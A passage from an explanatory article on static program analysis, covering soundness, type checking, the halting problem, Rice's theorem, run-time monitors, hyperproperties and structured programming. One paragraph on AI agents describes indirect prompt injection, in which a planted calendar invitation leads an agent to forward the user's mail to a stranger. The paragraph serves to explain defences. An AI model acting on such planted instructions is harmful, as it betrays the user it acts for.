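# Guaranteeing program behaviour by checking program text: types, structured code, ownership, and restrictions on AI agents

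## Program text, program behaviour and what a checker does

A computer program is a text in a formal language. A machine running the program performs actions such as opening files, adding numbers and sending messages, and it may or may not eventually stop. People who depend on software care mostly about these actions, but before the program runs they have only the text. Static program analysis, a branch of computer science, draws conclusions from the text, without running the program, about what the program can do. Compilers, which translate source text into machine instructions, have used it since the early 1960s to produce faster code (Møller and Schwartzbach, *Static Program Analysis*, 2025). Programmers now also use it to find errors or to show that certain kinds of error cannot occur.

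No method can answer every question about every program's behaviour by checking its text. Several families of methods avoid this limit by accepting only programs written in a form that guarantees the wanted behaviour. Type systems restrict which operations may apply to which values, structured programming restricts how a program may jump from one place in its text to another, and ownership rules restrict which parts of a program may use a piece of data, and for how long.

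### A five-line program

The following program is in Python, a widely used programming language.

```python
path = "notes.txt"
f = open(path)
text = f.read()
f.close()
print(text)
```

In one run, the program names a file, opens it, copies the contents into `text`, closes the file and prints what it read. In another, `notes.txt` does not exist, so the second line fails and the program stops there. In *Introduction*, the opening notes of a course on program analysis, Kalhauge calls the sequence of states that a machine passes through in one run a "trace", and takes the meaning of a program to be the set of all its possible traces. Here, "behaviour" likewise means everything the program might do, on any input and in any surroundings.

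A program has the property "never reads a closed file" if no trace contains a call to `read` on a file that the program has already closed. The call counts as a violation even if the system rejects it. This property is semantic, meaning it concerns what the program does when it runs. "Has five lines" and "contains the word `close`" are syntactic properties, meaning they concern the text itself, and a procedure that always finishes can check them by reading the text.

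Exchanging the third and fourth lines gives a program with the same five lines in a different order:

```python
path = "notes.txt"
f = open(path)
f.close()
text = f.read()
print(text)
```

This swapped program violates the property whenever the file exists. An old edition of the official Python tutorial shows the run stopping at the offending line with the message "ValueError: I/O operation on closed file". Python makes this check during the run, so it is a dynamic check. A static check happens before the run and uses only the program text. The dynamic check is easy because by then the machine holds one particular file in one particular state. But it covers only the run in progress, and it detects the violation only once the program reaches the bad step.

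Testing has the same limitation, since a test is a run. Møller and Schwartzbach give a short program in the language C that is full of memory errors, none of which occurs unless the program's argument count happens to be 42. A tester who never tries that number sees nothing wrong. (The compiler they tried, with its usual warnings switched on, reported nothing either, so a static tool has to be looking for the right thing.)

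The specification, a precise statement of the property that a check should guarantee, defines what counts as the right thing. A program analysis textbook from the University of Washington defines a correct program as one that implements its specification, so correctness depends on what somebody wrote down. Small differences in wording can change which programs count as correct. Among the properties that programmers may want to check, Møller and Schwartzbach list whether `open` is always called before `read`. The swapped program satisfies this property as worded, because it calls `open` before `read`, even though it calls `close` in between. The property "never reads a closed file" rules out that mistake but not others, since a program that opens a file and never closes it satisfies the property, as does an empty program.

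### Accepting and rejecting

A checker is a procedure that reads a program and accepts or rejects it. Here is a crude one for the file property, which might be called the line-order rule: reject the program if a line containing `close` stands anywhere above a line containing `read`, and accept it otherwise. A few lines of code could apply this rule to any text. It gives the right verdict on both programs so far. It is wrong about this one:

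```python
path = "notes.txt"
f = open(path)
if len(path) > 100:
    f.close()
text = f.read()
```

The name `notes.txt` has nine characters, so the program never closes the file and the read is harmless. The rule rejects it all the same. Rejecting a program that does have the property is a false alarm. The rule also errs in the other direction:

```python
f = open("notes.txt")
for i in range(2):
    text = f.read()
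    f.close()
```

The rule accepts this program because no `close` appears above a `read`. But the loop runs its two indented lines twice, so on the second pass the program reads a file it closed on the first.

Every program falls into one of four boxes. Bertrand Meyer, in Communications of the ACM, proposes plain names for them to replace the "true positives" and "false negatives" that many authors use. In the table, "safe" means that the program never reads a closed file.

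| | Safe program | Unsafe program |
|---|---|---|
| **Checker accepts** | Correct acceptance: the original five lines | Missed violation: the program with the loop |
| **Checker rejects** | False alarm: the program that tests the length of the path | Caught violation: the swapped program |

A checker is sound if every program it accepts has the property, which means the "missed violation" box is empty. It is complete if it accepts every program that has the property, which means the "false alarm" box is empty. The line-order rule is neither sound nor complete.

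Soundness and completeness are each trivial to achieve without the other. Meyer points out that a checker that rejects every program is sound, and one that accepts every program is complete. A claim of soundness is therefore of little use without knowing how many good programs the checker rejects. Meyer measures this by precision, the share of rejections that are deserved. If a checker rejects twenty programs and fifteen of them really can read a closed file, its precision is 15/20, or 75 per cent. He considers missed violations worse in principle, but adds that false alarms are nearly as damaging in practice, because programmers stop reading the output of a tool that keeps raising them.

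One way to catch the missed violation in the table is to make the line-order rule reject any program that contains a loop, but the rule would then also reject many harmless programs. To be sound, it would have to ban other constructs too, such as functions that close the file elsewhere in the text and second names for the `close` operation. Each ban reduces how much of the language the rule covers and makes its results for the rest more reliable.

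The meanings of "sound" and "complete" vary across this literature. The coding guidelines of the Software Engineering Institute (SEI) at Carnegie Mellon University use them the other way round, so a tool is "complete" if it finds every violation and "sound" if it raises no false alarms. Møller and Schwartzbach observe that people call a verification tool sound when it misses no errors of the kind it looks for, but call an automated testing tool sound when every error it reports is genuine.

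Smaragdakis, in lecture slides from the University of Athens, covers the different uses of "sound" with one definition from logic, that an analysis is sound if whatever it claims is true. For a type checker, the claim is that a program is free of certain errors, so a sound one misses none of those errors. For a bug finder, the claim is that a bug exists, so a sound one raises no false alarms. In practice, it is more useful to ask whether a tool's makers say it has no missed violations or no false alarms than whether they call it sound.

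Whether an error counts as a false alarm or a missed violation depends on what the tool is for. In an example of Meyer's, an analysis wrongly concludes that some piece of code can never run. This is a false alarm and a minor nuisance if the tool only comments on programming style. If the tool is a compiler that deletes unreachable code, the same error is a missed violation, and the compiler will delete something the program needs.

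### What "well-typed" means

The first checker most programmers meet is a type checker. A type is a label for a kind of value, such as `int` for whole numbers or `str` for text. The manual of mypy (2026), a static type checker for Python, opens with a program that asks the user for a favourite number and then adds 1 to the reply. The reply is text, even if the user types digits, and Python cannot add a number to text. Mypy reports this error before the program runs, so the programmer does not have to discover it when the program fails.

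Mypy reaches its verdicts by typing rules, conditions that it applies to each piece of the text in turn. Programmers call a text that satisfies the rules "well-typed". The phrase sounds like a description of behaviour, and a pair of small programs shows that it is not one. Here is the first:

```python
n = 1
print(n)
n = "x"
print(n)
```

And the second:

```python
n: int | str = 1
print(n)
n = "x"
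print(n)
```

Both print `1` and then `x`. The only difference is the note `int | str` in the second program, which declares that `n` may hold either a number or text. Such notes do not change how the program runs, and the manual compares them to comments. But mypy rejects the program without the note and accepts the one with it. Mypy's *Type inference and type annotations* explains that when a variable has no note, mypy takes its type from its first value, here `int`. It then reports the later assignment with the message "Incompatible types in assignment". Code Maven's *Changing types* shows the same behaviour with a slightly longer script, which Python runs without error but mypy reports an error at each change of type.

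So if the property to be guaranteed is that no operation fails because a value has the wrong type, the rejection is a false alarm, although the checker is working as designed. The rule that a variable keeps one type is simple to apply and predict, and a programmer can easily satisfy it by adding an annotation or using two variables. Mypy's *Common issues and solutions* also describes a setting that suppresses the error in several such cases. Changing the setting can change whether a program passes without changing its text or behaviour, because whether a program is well-typed depends on the checker's rules as well as the text.

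The rules also determine what the checker's verdict covers. Mypy accepts the swapped program from earlier, which reads a file after closing it. Pilgrim (2010) notes in *Dive Into Python 3* that closing a file does not destroy the object that represents it. `f` is a file object with a `read` operation both before and after `close`, and its type does not record the change. A guarantee against type errors covers only type errors. To catch reads of closed files, a checker needs rules that also track the file's state.

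### The trusted base

A proof of soundness covers a checker only as it is described on paper. In practice, a guarantee depends on its trusted base, which is everything that must work correctly for the guarantee to hold: the program that implements the checker, the libraries that the checked code calls, the language's machinery for running programs, the operating system and the hardware. The trusted base also includes parts that are easy to overlook, such as the stub files that Python programmers can supply to mypy. A stub file lists the types of a module's functions, and mypy reads it instead of the module. If a stub lists a function as returning text when it actually returns a number, mypy will accept programs that fail when they run.

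### The halting problem

Why not simply build a checker that is both sound and complete? Part of the answer is that a short text can pose a very hard question. Imagine a program that asks its user for three whole numbers, positive or negative, opens a file, closes it, and then reads from it only if the cubes of the three numbers add up to 42. The program is safe if no such numbers exist. From 1954 to 2019 nobody knew whether they did; Møller and Schwartzbach, who use the same sum as an example, report that finding the answer took more than a million hours of computing. (They do exist, so the program is unsafe.)

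Hard questions may still yield to effort. The halting problem does not. It asks for a procedure that takes any program, together with an input, and always answers correctly whether the program would eventually stop when run on that input. The proof that there is none fits into a few lines. Suppose somebody has written such a procedure, called `halts`, and that it always returns an answer: true if the program it examines would stop, false if it would run for ever. Then anyone can write this program, which takes no input:

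```python
def contrary():
    while halts(contrary):
        pass
```

`pass` does nothing, and `while` repeats it for as long as the condition is true. If `halts` reports that `contrary` stops, `contrary` loops for ever. If `halts` reports that `contrary` runs for ever, the loop ends at once and `contrary` stops. Either result is wrong, so `halts` cannot exist. The argument does not depend on how `halts` works, so a cleverer method of reading programs would not help.

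Strachey (1965) published essentially this version in a letter to *The Computer Journal*, explaining that Alan Turing had once given him a proof but that he had forgotten the details. Textbooks usually credit the theorem to Turing's 1936 paper. Hamkins and Nenu (2024), in *Did Turing prove the undecidability of the halting problem?*, found neither the halting problem nor this proof in that paper. The first clear statements they know of are in books by Stephen Kleene (1952) and Martin Davis (1958), and Davis gave the problem its name. Turing did prove that no procedure can decide whether a given program will ever print a given symbol. That question is equivalent to the halting problem, and Hamkins and Nenu think it is fair to give him qualified credit.

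The theorem rules out a procedure that is right about every program, but one can still settle the question for particular programs or build a tool that sometimes answers "don't know". A checker that must accept or reject can treat "don't know" as a rejection, in which case it remains sound but raises false alarms. The slides for Brown University's *Topics in Programming Languages* describe the aim as algorithms "that are wrong in a predictable way". Rice's theorem of 1953 extends the impossibility from halting to practically every question about behaviour, including whether a program ever reads a closed file.

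### Agents, tool calls and prompt injection

An AI agent is a language model connected to tools, such as a calendar, an e-mail account or a command line, by an ordinary program that carries out the model's requests. *Defense Against Indirect Prompt Injection via Tool Result Parsing* (2026) gives the example of a user who asks how many appointments she has today. The model responds with a tool call, a piece of structured text that names a tool and supplies its arguments, in this case a date. The program executes the call and adds the result to the model's next input. *AttriGuard* (2026) describes this cycle as repeating until the model's output contains no more calls. The model receives both the user's request and the tool results as text, and models cannot reliably distinguish instructions from data that looks like instructions. Prompt injection exploits this weakness. *The Claws in Plain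 Sight* (2026) distinguishes direct injection, in which the attacker addresses the model himself, from indirect injection, in which he plants instructions in a web page, document or e-mail that the agent will read later. For example, a calendar invitation might include an instruction to forward the user's mail to a stranger, and the model's next tool call might do it. *AgentSys* (2026) stresses that the user has done nothing wrong in such a case. The damage can go well beyond bad text, since agents often have access to files and can execute code. But because a tool call is itself text, a checker can read it before it runs and refuse it, for example if the tool is not on an allowlist of permitted tools. A sandbox limits what the call can reach once it runs.

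## Decide whether the property can be checked at all

Before writing any rules, the builder of a checker needs to know whether an exact checker can exist for the chosen property. Rice's theorem rules one out for most properties of behaviour, but its textbook form does not cover the file property, which needs a short separate proof.

### Rice's theorem and its proof

A program that takes a whole number and, if it stops, returns a whole number computes a partial function. The function has a value for exactly those inputs on which the program stops. Different programs can compute the same function. *Lecture Notes on Algorithmic Information Theory* (2025) notes that infinitely many programs compute the successor function, which adds 1 to its input.

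A property of programs is extensional if it depends only on the function a program computes. For example, "computes the successor function" is extensional, but "contains a loop" is not. A property is non-trivial if some programs have it and others lack it. Rice's theorem states that, for any non-trivial extensional property, no procedure can always terminate and correctly answer whether an arbitrary program has it. *On the Semantics of Intensionality and Intensional Recursion* (2017) states the theorem in symbols. If φₑ is the function that program number e computes, and F is any set of computable partial functions except the empty set and the set of all of them, then the set {e : φₑ ∈ F} is undecidable.

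*Classes of Recursively Enumerable Sets and Their Decision Problems* (Rice, 1953) treats a program as a description of the set of all numbers it outputs. Textbooks usually use functions instead of sets.

The usual proof turns a decider for the property into a solution of the halting problem. Suppose somebody has a procedure `is_successor` that is right about every program. To find out whether a program `p` stops on input `x`, write the following, where `run(p, x)` executes `p` on `x` and discards the result:

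```python
def t(n):
    run(p, x)
    return n + 1
```

If `p` stops on `x`, then `t` returns n + 1 for every n, so it computes the successor function. If `p` runs forever, `t` never returns. So `is_successor(t)` is true exactly when `p` stops on `x`. `is_successor` uses only the text of `t`, so `t` doesn't have to be run.

The same construction works for every non-trivial extensional property P:

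1. Suppose a procedure `decide` always terminates and correctly answers whether a program has P.
2. Take a program that loops for ever on every input, and assume that it lacks P. (If it has P, use the property "lacks P" instead and swap the answers of `decide`.)
3. Because P is non-trivial, some program `b` has it.
4. For any `p` and `x`, write a program `t` that first executes `run(p, x)` and then returns `b(n)`.
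5. If `p` stops on `x`, `t` computes the same function as `b`, so it has P. If `p` does not stop, `t` computes the same function as the looping program, so it lacks P.
6. `decide(t)` therefore answers whether `p` stops on `x`. Since no procedure can do that for all `p` and `x`, `decide` cannot exist.

A shorter proof uses a program like `contrary` from the previous section. The program can obtain its own text, apply `decide` to it, and then behave like a program of the kind opposite to `decide`'s answer.

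### A separate proof for the file property

"Never reads a closed file" is not extensional, as these two functions show:

```python
def a(n):
    return n + 1

def b(n):
    f = open("notes.txt")
    f.close()
    try:
        f.read()
    except ValueError:
        pass
    return n + 1
```

Whenever `notes.txt` exists, both return n + 1, because the `except` line catches the error that Python raises. Only `b` reads a closed file. A theorem about the functions that programs compute treats the two as identical, so it does not settle whether a checker could distinguish them. Introductions sometimes blur this distinction. *A Programming Language Oriented Approach to Computability* (2014) gives "the machine leaves this part of the memory untouched" as an example of a property that Rice proved undecidable, then states the theorem for input and output only. The property is undecidable, but this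 does not follow from the theorem as stated.

What is missing is a second reduction. Let `p` be a program that only does arithmetic and touches no files. The halting problem is just as unsolvable for such programs. Now write:

```python
run(p, x)
f = open("notes.txt")
f.close()
f.read()
```

If `p` stops on `x`, the program then reads a closed file in any run where `notes.txt` exists. If `p` runs forever, the program never gets past its first line. The program therefore has the file property exactly when `p` does not stop, so an exact checker for it would solve the halting problem.

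The last three lines could be any forbidden action. Hamlen, Morrisett and Schneider (2006) make the general point in *Computability Classes for Enforcement Mechanisms* that ensuring an arbitrary program never performs some prohibited action is as hard as the halting problem. Their example is a policy against writing to the boot sector of a disk, which holds the code that starts the computer.

But some questions about behaviour are decidable. Hamlen and colleagues mention "terminates within 100 steps". In 100 steps a program can read at most 100 symbols of input, so a checker can simulate it for 100 steps on every input of that length. Rice's theorem does not apply because the number of steps is not part of the function that a program computes. This check is impractical, however, because even with only two possible symbols there are 2¹⁰⁰ such inputs, about 10³⁰. Real computers have finite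 memory, so in principle one could also detect an endless loop by waiting for the machine to repeat a state, but this can be impractical too, since a single kilobyte of memory has 2⁸¹⁹² possible states.

### Infinitely many false alarms

If a checker for the file property is sound and always terminates, it must raise false alarms, since otherwise it would decide the property. It must also raise infinitely many. Suppose it wrongly rejected only a thousand programs. Somebody could store those programs in a table and add a step that accepts any program found there. The combined checker would still be sound and always terminate, but it would raise no false alarms, which is impossible. This argument holds even though nobody may know which programs belong in the table, because the proof shows that no exact checker exists, whether or not anyone could find it.

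The argument also works if a terminating test for the false alarms replaces the table. So no such test exists, and no tool can sort all of a checker's false alarms from its deserved rejections. This is a stronger result than having infinitely many false alarms, since adding comments to one wrongly rejected program already produces infinitely many. There is also no best sound checker, because using a table to accept one more wrongly rejected program improves any of them.

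Rice's theorem does not set a minimum share of useful programs that a checker must reject. *Software is infrastructure* (2025) illustrates the incompleteness of practical type systems with `fun x -> x x`, a function that applies its argument to itself. Most programmers could work for years without wanting to write it. If a tool rejects half of the sensible programs its users write, the cause is the tool's design.

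### A common misreading

Rice's theorem, like the halting problem, leaves room for proofs about particular programs. Rice wrote in 1953, "Of course there will exist special methods for particular functions." People sometimes take the theorem to mean that nobody can establish anything about a program by reading it. The forum post *Rice’s Theorem says that AIs can’t determine much* concludes from it that one agent could not reliably find out from another's source code how the other makes decisions. One reply objects that the same reasoning would imply that nobody can show any property of any program. Another gives the example of a program consisting of "return 0", which clearly halts.

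Undecidability applies to an infinite collection of programs, not to a single program. For the program in the previous section that reads a closed file only if three cubes add up to 42, either "always answer safe" or "always answer unsafe" was a correct procedure, even while nobody knew which. But no single procedure can give the right answer for every program in the whole infinite collection. There may well be one for a smaller collection. For example, every program made up only of additions and assignments, with no loops or function calls, stops, and a checker can easily recognise such programs.

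### Tolerate false alarms

Someone building a checker has four options: accept false alarms, restrict the language, require a proof with each program, or check at run time. Practical systems combine these. For example, the Java virtual machine, which runs Java programs, checks some type rules before a program starts and others while it runs.

Tolerating false alarms means replacing the property with a stronger one that a procedure can decide. For example, a checker that accepts only programs that stop within 100 steps guarantees that every program it accepts will stop, but it wrongly rejects a program that stops after 101. A checker for files could improve on the line-order rule by working out, for each line, whether the file might be closed when the program gets there, treating both outcomes of every `if` as possible. It would reject the program with the loop, because the file is open on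 the first pass and closed on the second. It would still reject the program that tests the length of its path, because it does not work out that the test fails.

The drawback is that programmers must rewrite good programs to satisfy the checker. Makers of bug-finding tools often choose to miss some violations rather than raise false alarms, so that developers keep reading the reports. *Static Code Analysis with CodeChecker* (2024) favours this choice for practical tools and notes that reducing one kind of error usually increases the other. *Software is infrastructure* describes a compromise called "soundy" analysis, which is sound except in some cases that experts know about and consider unavoidable. Non-experts need to see a list of these exceptions before relying on such a tool.

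### Restrict the language

Rice's theorem does not apply to a property that every program in a language has, so a designer can guarantee a property by creating a language in which every program must have it. Turner proposed doing this for termination in *Elementary Strong Functional Programming* (1995) and *Total Functional Programming* (2004). In a total language, every program either stops or, if it is meant to run forever, keeps producing output.

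Turner wanted, in part, to let programmers reason about programs as they would about equations. *Total functional programming* (Seo, 2015) gives the example of a function defined as `loop n = 1 + loop n`. Setting `n` to 0 and subtracting `loop 0` from both sides gives 0 = 1. The algebra fails because `loop 0` never produces a number to subtract. Turner excludes such definitions by allowing a function to call itself only on a smaller part of its argument. For example, a function that adds up a list may call itself on the list without its first element, and since the list is finite, the calls must end. To allow for programs that should not end, such as servers, Turner separates finite data from codata, which may be infinite, like an endless stream of replies. A program that produces codata must deliver each successive item in a finite time.

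One drawback of a total language is that it cannot express some functions, even though a method that always stops can compute them. If we number the language's programs 0, 1, 2 and so on, we can define d(n) as one more than the result of program n on input n. Every program stops, so computing d(n) always stops too. But d differs from program n at input n, for every n, so no program in the language computes d. For the same reason, a total language cannot express its own interpreter.

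Other functions remain expressible, but only by extremely long programs. Manuel Blum proved in 1967 that the gap in program length between a total language and a general-purpose one can exceed any computable bound. For any size N, let g(n) be one more than the largest result that any total program of at most N characters gives on input n. There are finitely many such programs, so the total language can express g with a program that contains them all. No total program of N characters or fewer can compute g, because g(n) is always larger than that program's result. A general-purpose language needs only a fixed-length interpreter for the total language and a formula for N. The ten-character formula `10**10**10`, for example, stands for a 1 followed by ten billion zeros.

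Nobody would write g for a practical purpose, and the restriction may be only a small burden in everyday programming. The University of Oxford's *Turner, Bird, Eratosthenes* reports Turner's observation that most programs already have the form his discipline requires, though this is an experienced programmer's impression rather than a count.

A total language settles termination and much less besides. The slides from Brown University state that Rice's theorem holds only for Turing-complete languages, those that can express every computable function. As examples of languages outside its reach they give the database query language SQL and the configuration language Dhall, which refuses a function that calls itself. The claim is right about the halting problem but too generous about other properties. Rice's paper closes by remarking that the situation does not improve if one allows only functions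 defined on every input, or even only primitive recursive functions, which one can compute using loops whose number of repetitions is fixed before they start. The file property shows why:

```python
def q(k):
    f = open("notes.txt")
    f.close()
    if stops_within(p, x, k):
        f.read()
```

Here `stops_within` runs `p` on `x` for at most `k` steps, so `q` always stops. But `q` reads a closed file for some value of `k` exactly when `p` stops on `x`, so an exact check over all inputs is still impossible. To guarantee the file property by restriction, the language must restrict how programs use files. For example, it could have no `close` operation, close each file automatically at the end of the block that opened it, and forbid using the file outside that block.

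### Demand a proof with the program

Finding a proof can be arbitrarily hard, but checking one is routine, so a builder can leave finding the proof to the program's supplier. *Enforceable Security Policies* (Schneider, 2000) describes George Necula's proof-carrying code of 1997, in which a program comes with a proof that it obeys a policy. The recipient checks the proof mechanically before running the program, and then doesn't need to enforce the policy during the run.

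For the program that tests the length of its path, the proof might go as follows. When the program reaches the test, `path` is `notes.txt`, which has nine characters. Nine is not greater than 100, so Python skips the `close`, and the file is still open at the `read`. The recipient's checker only has to confirm that each step follows from earlier ones by a fixed rule, which it can do in a finite time because the proof is finite. It can accept a program that the cruder rules reject, without having to find the proof itself. The trusted base includes the checker and its rules about how instructions behave, but not the supplier or the tools that found the proof.

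Most of the effort falls on the supplier. In Necula's original version, people had to construct the proofs by hand. Schneider notes that for some policies a compiler can generate them from programs in a type-safe language, which makes the method similar to type checking.

For any fixed set of sound proof rules, some good programs have no proof. Suppose every program with the file property had one. A procedure could then alternate between trying possible proofs and running the program on more and more inputs for longer and longer, and it would eventually find either a proof or a violation. It would therefore decide the file property, which is impossible. So a recipient who insists on proofs also raises false alarms.

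### Check at run time

A run-time monitor watches a program's actions and intervenes when the next one would break a rule, so it doesn't need to predict what the program will do. Python's own check for closed files works this way. If a program calls `run(p, x)` and then reads from a closed file, the check catches the read when the program reaches it, which happens only if `p` stops.

Hamlen and colleagues compare static checks with run-time monitors. A static check adds nothing to the running time, while a monitor usually slows the program down. A monitor that stops a program partway may also leave half-finished work that somebody has to undo. But some policies are simpler to enforce during the run, which lowers the risk of mistakes in the enforcement code.

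The more often a monitor has to act, the more it slows the program. Schneider points out that supervising access to files adds little overhead, because each access already passes through the operating system, whereas supervising every machine instruction could slow the program greatly. He and Erlingsson built prototypes that insert the monitor's tests into a program's code, for Intel processors and for the Java virtual machine. Analysis of the program before it runs can remove tests that could never fail.

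### Which policies a monitor can enforce

Schneider considers monitors that observe a program's steps and can do nothing except stop it. For such a monitor to enforce a policy, the policy must meet three conditions:

- It judges each run on its own, without reference to other runs.
- If it forbids the beginning of a run, it forbids every continuation. The program might end at any moment, so a monitor cannot let a bad beginning pass in the hope that later steps will put it right.
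- Every run that it forbids has already broken it after some finite number of steps.

Policies that meet these conditions are safety properties, which require that something bad never happens, for example that a program never reads a closed file. A liveness property requires that something good eventually happens, for example that a server answers every request. A monitor can never declare a violation of that property, because an unanswered request might still be answered later. *Hyperproperties* (Clarkson and Schneider, 2009) recalls a theorem that every property of individual runs is a combination of a safety property and a liveness property. A builder can therefore split such a requirement into a part that a monitor might enforce and a part that needs another method.

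One of Schneider's examples is a policy that a program must not send messages after it has read a file. The monitor needs to remember one fact:

```python
has_read = False

def allow(action):
    global has_read
    if action == "read_file":
        has_read = True
    return not (has_read and action == "send")
```

The system calls `allow` before each action and stops the program if it returns false. Schneider calls the underlying device a security automaton, a set of states with rules for moving between them. This one has two states, "no file read yet" and "file read", and the second has no rule for a send.

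Small changes in a policy can decide whether a monitor is able to enforce it:

| Policy | Enforceable by stopping the program? | Reason |
|---|---|---|
| No message after a file read | Yes | The monitor can stop the program before the send |
| Every request eventually gets an answer | No | No finite delay proves a violation |
| Nobody waits longer than a set number of seconds | No | Stopping the program does not stop the clock |
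| Nobody waits longer than a set number of program steps | Yes | Stopping the program stops the count |

Only safety properties can be enforced, but the limit in seconds is a safety property that cannot be. Basin et al. (2012) refine Schneider's account by distinguishing actions a monitor can prevent from those it can only observe, such as the tick of a clock.

A monitor can also fail to ensure that a customer gets what the policy seems to guarantee, because stopping is always permitted. In another of Schneider's examples, the policy forbids a seller who has taken payment from doing anything except delivering the service. The monitor can block every other action, but the seller's program can comply by doing nothing.

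The guarantee also requires the monitor to receive every relevant action. Schneider warns that a system may contain many ways to send a message, some buried deep inside it. If the definition of "send" omits one, the two-state monitor will let through messages sent that way. The program must also be unable to alter the monitor's memory. In the code above, a program that could set `has_read` back to `False` would escape the policy.

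Hamlen and colleagues found that the class of policies earlier researchers thought monitors could enforce is only an upper limit. That class contains every policy for which some procedure eventually detects every violating program, but detection can come too late for a monitor to prevent the violation. Suppose a service lends a resource to one program at a time and cannot take it back. When a program announces that it has finished, the service lends the resource to the next one. If the first program then uses the resource again, the monitor can recognise the violation, but two programs already hold the resource. To prevent this, the monitor would have to work out at the time of the announcement whether the program might ever use the resource again, which is the halting problem once more.

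They also show that rewriting a program can enforce some policies that monitoring it cannot. A system may need to hide the existence of a secret file, so that a program behaves exactly as it would if the file were not there. No method can decide whether an arbitrary program already behaves that way, and no monitor can enforce the policy. But a tool can rewrite the program so that every directory listing it receives omits the file. A program that would have ignored the file behaves as before, and one that would have reacted to it no longer can, so the tool doesn't need to determine which kind it was given.

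### Policies that compare runs

The secret-file policy, like many confidentiality policies, compares what a program does with what it would have done in other circumstances. Noninterference, for example, requires that the actions of users with access to secrets not affect what other users observe.

Two programs each read a secret bit, 0 or 1, and then print a digit in public. One always prints 1, and the other prints the secret. When the secret is 1, both programs read a 1 and print a 1. A monitor that observes only this run must treat them alike, although the first program is harmless and the second reveals the secret. Telling them apart requires knowing what each would have printed if the secret had been 0.

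Clarkson and Schneider introduced the term "hyperproperty" for policies on the whole set of a system's possible runs. An ordinary property is a set P of permitted runs, and a system whose set of runs is T satisfies it if T ⊆ P. A hyperproperty H is a set of permitted sets of runs, and the system satisfies it if T ∈ H. Removing runs from a system can never break an ordinary property, which is why a monitor may safely cut runs short, but it can break a hyperproperty. Clarkson and Schneider describe a system that freely chooses to output 0, 1 or the value of a secret bit. The possible outputs are 0 and 1 whatever the secret is, so the set of outputs reveals nothing about it. If the runs that use the first two choices are removed, the system always outputs the secret.

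Like secrecy, a limit of one second on the average response time over all runs is a hyperproperty, since a slow run may be acceptable if the others are fast enough. If the limit applied to the average within each run instead, it would be an ordinary property.

A monitor can still enforce a stricter policy that can be checked on each run separately and that implies the desired policy. For example, if a secret is stored in a file and can leave only through messages, forbidding all messages after a file read prevents a leak, but it also blocks messages that have nothing to do with the secret.

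Static methods have an advantage here, because the text of a program describes all of its runs at once. In self-composition, the checker examines a system made of two copies of the original, so a comparison between two runs becomes an ordinary property of one combined run. Schneider's *Verifying Hyperproperties with Temporal Logic of Actions (TLA)* extends the technique to a larger class of policies, including those hyperproperties known to express security conditions, so that existing tools for checking industrial designs can handle them. *Temporal Logics for Hyperproperties* (2014) instead extends the usual specification languages to refer to several runs together, and presents a prototype checker for part of the resulting language. Information-flow type systems reject programs in which secret data could influence public output, but they also reject some programs that leak nothing.

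## Restrict the control flow: structured programming and verified bytecode

One of the oldest ways to restrict a language is to limit its control flow, the order in which a program's statements run. Early languages relied on `goto`, a statement that jumps to any labelled line. Structured programming replaces it with a few constructs: statements in sequence, a choice between two pieces of code, a loop, and a procedure call.

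### Dijkstra's argument

The best-known attack on `goto` is Dijkstra's *A Case against the GO TO Statement*, which Communications of the ACM printed in March 1968 as "Go To Statement Considered Harmful". It opens by remarking that programmers who use more `goto` statements are worse programmers. Dijkstra gives no data for this, and his main argument does not need any. He argues that people are good at grasping fixed relations but bad at picturing processes in time, so a program's text should show as directly as possible how far its execution has progressed.

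Dijkstra imagines stopping a run after an arbitrary action and asks what one would need to know to bring a second run to the same point. If the program has only assignments and choices, one position in the text is enough. If it has procedures, one also needs the position of each call that has not yet returned. For each loop in progress, one needs the number of the current repetition. The program text and the run determine all these positions and counts, and the programmer cannot set or alter them.

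We can interpret the value of a variable only if we know how far the run has progressed. Suppose a program counts the people in a room by adding 1 to `n` whenever somebody enters. Just after a person comes in, before the program does the addition, `n` is one too low. In a structured program, it is easy to say where in the text this happens. If a program can jump from anywhere to anywhere, the only way to describe the run's progress may be to count the actions since the start, and there is usually no simple way to describe the action counts at which `n` is one too low.

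### Structured programs compute the same functions

Giving up `goto` does not reduce what programs can compute. *Complete set of control statements* defines a set of control statements as complete if every program in the language has an equivalent that uses only that set. Böhm and Jacopini proved in 1966 that sequence, `if` and `while` form a complete set, and Rapaport (2001) notes that their paper includes an algorithm for converting programs to this form.

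Here is a small program with jumps. It adds up the numbers a user types until one is negative, with `total` starting at 0.

```
1  n = next number typed
2  if n < 0 goto 5
3  total = total + n
4  goto 1
5  print total
```

A simpler conversion than the one in the 1966 paper uses an extra variable to hold the number of the next line:

```python
total = 0
where = 1
while where != 6:
    if where == 1:
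        n = int(input())
        where = 2
    elif where == 2:
        if n < 0:
            where = 5
        else:
            where = 3
    elif where == 3:
        total = total + n
        where = 4
    elif where == 4:
        where = 1
    else:
        print(total)
        where = 6
```

The same method works for any program with numbered lines. The result has no `goto`, but it is no easier to follow. Each pass of the loop executes one line of the original program, so the repetition number only counts the actions since the start. Dijkstra advised against mechanical conversion because the result is unlikely to be clearer than the original. A programmer would instead read the first number before the loop and each later number at the end of a pass, with `while n >= 0` as the condition.

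The conversion is mechanical and preserves behaviour, so an exact checker for structured programs would also give an exact checker for programs with jumps. Banning `goto` therefore does not remove the undecidability that Rice's theorem and the file property illustrate, and it does not by itself guarantee anything about what a program does.

### Hoare's rules and the loop invariant

What the restriction provides is a method of proof that follows the text. Hoare, in *An Axiomatic Basis for Computer Programming* (1969), introduced a notation for claims about a piece of code, which people now usually write as {P} S {R}. It means that if P is true before S runs, and S finishes, then R is true afterwards. Each construct has its own rule:

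| To prove | Show |
|---|---|
| {P} `x = e` {R} | P implies the statement obtained from R by replacing x with e |
| {P} S, then T {R} | {P} S {M} and {M} T {R}, for some statement M |
| {P} if B, then S, else T {R} | {P and B} S {R} and {P and not B} T {R} |
| {P} while B, do S {P and not B} | {P and B} S {P} |

The first row combines Hoare's rule for assignment with another of his rules, which lets a prover assume more at the start or claim less at the end. The 1969 paper has no rule for choice, so the third row comes from later accounts.

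In the rule for loops, P is the loop invariant, a statement that each pass leaves true if it was true before the pass. Take this program, where `n` is a whole number and at least 0:

```python
i = 0
s = 0
while i < n:
    i = i + 1
    s = s + i
```

The claim is that it ends with s = 1 + 2 + … + n. A suitable invariant is "s = 1 + 2 + … + i, and i ≤ n", where the sum is 0 if i is 0. The proof has three steps:

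1. Before the loop, i and s are both 0. The invariant then says that 0 = 0 and 0 ≤ n, which is true.
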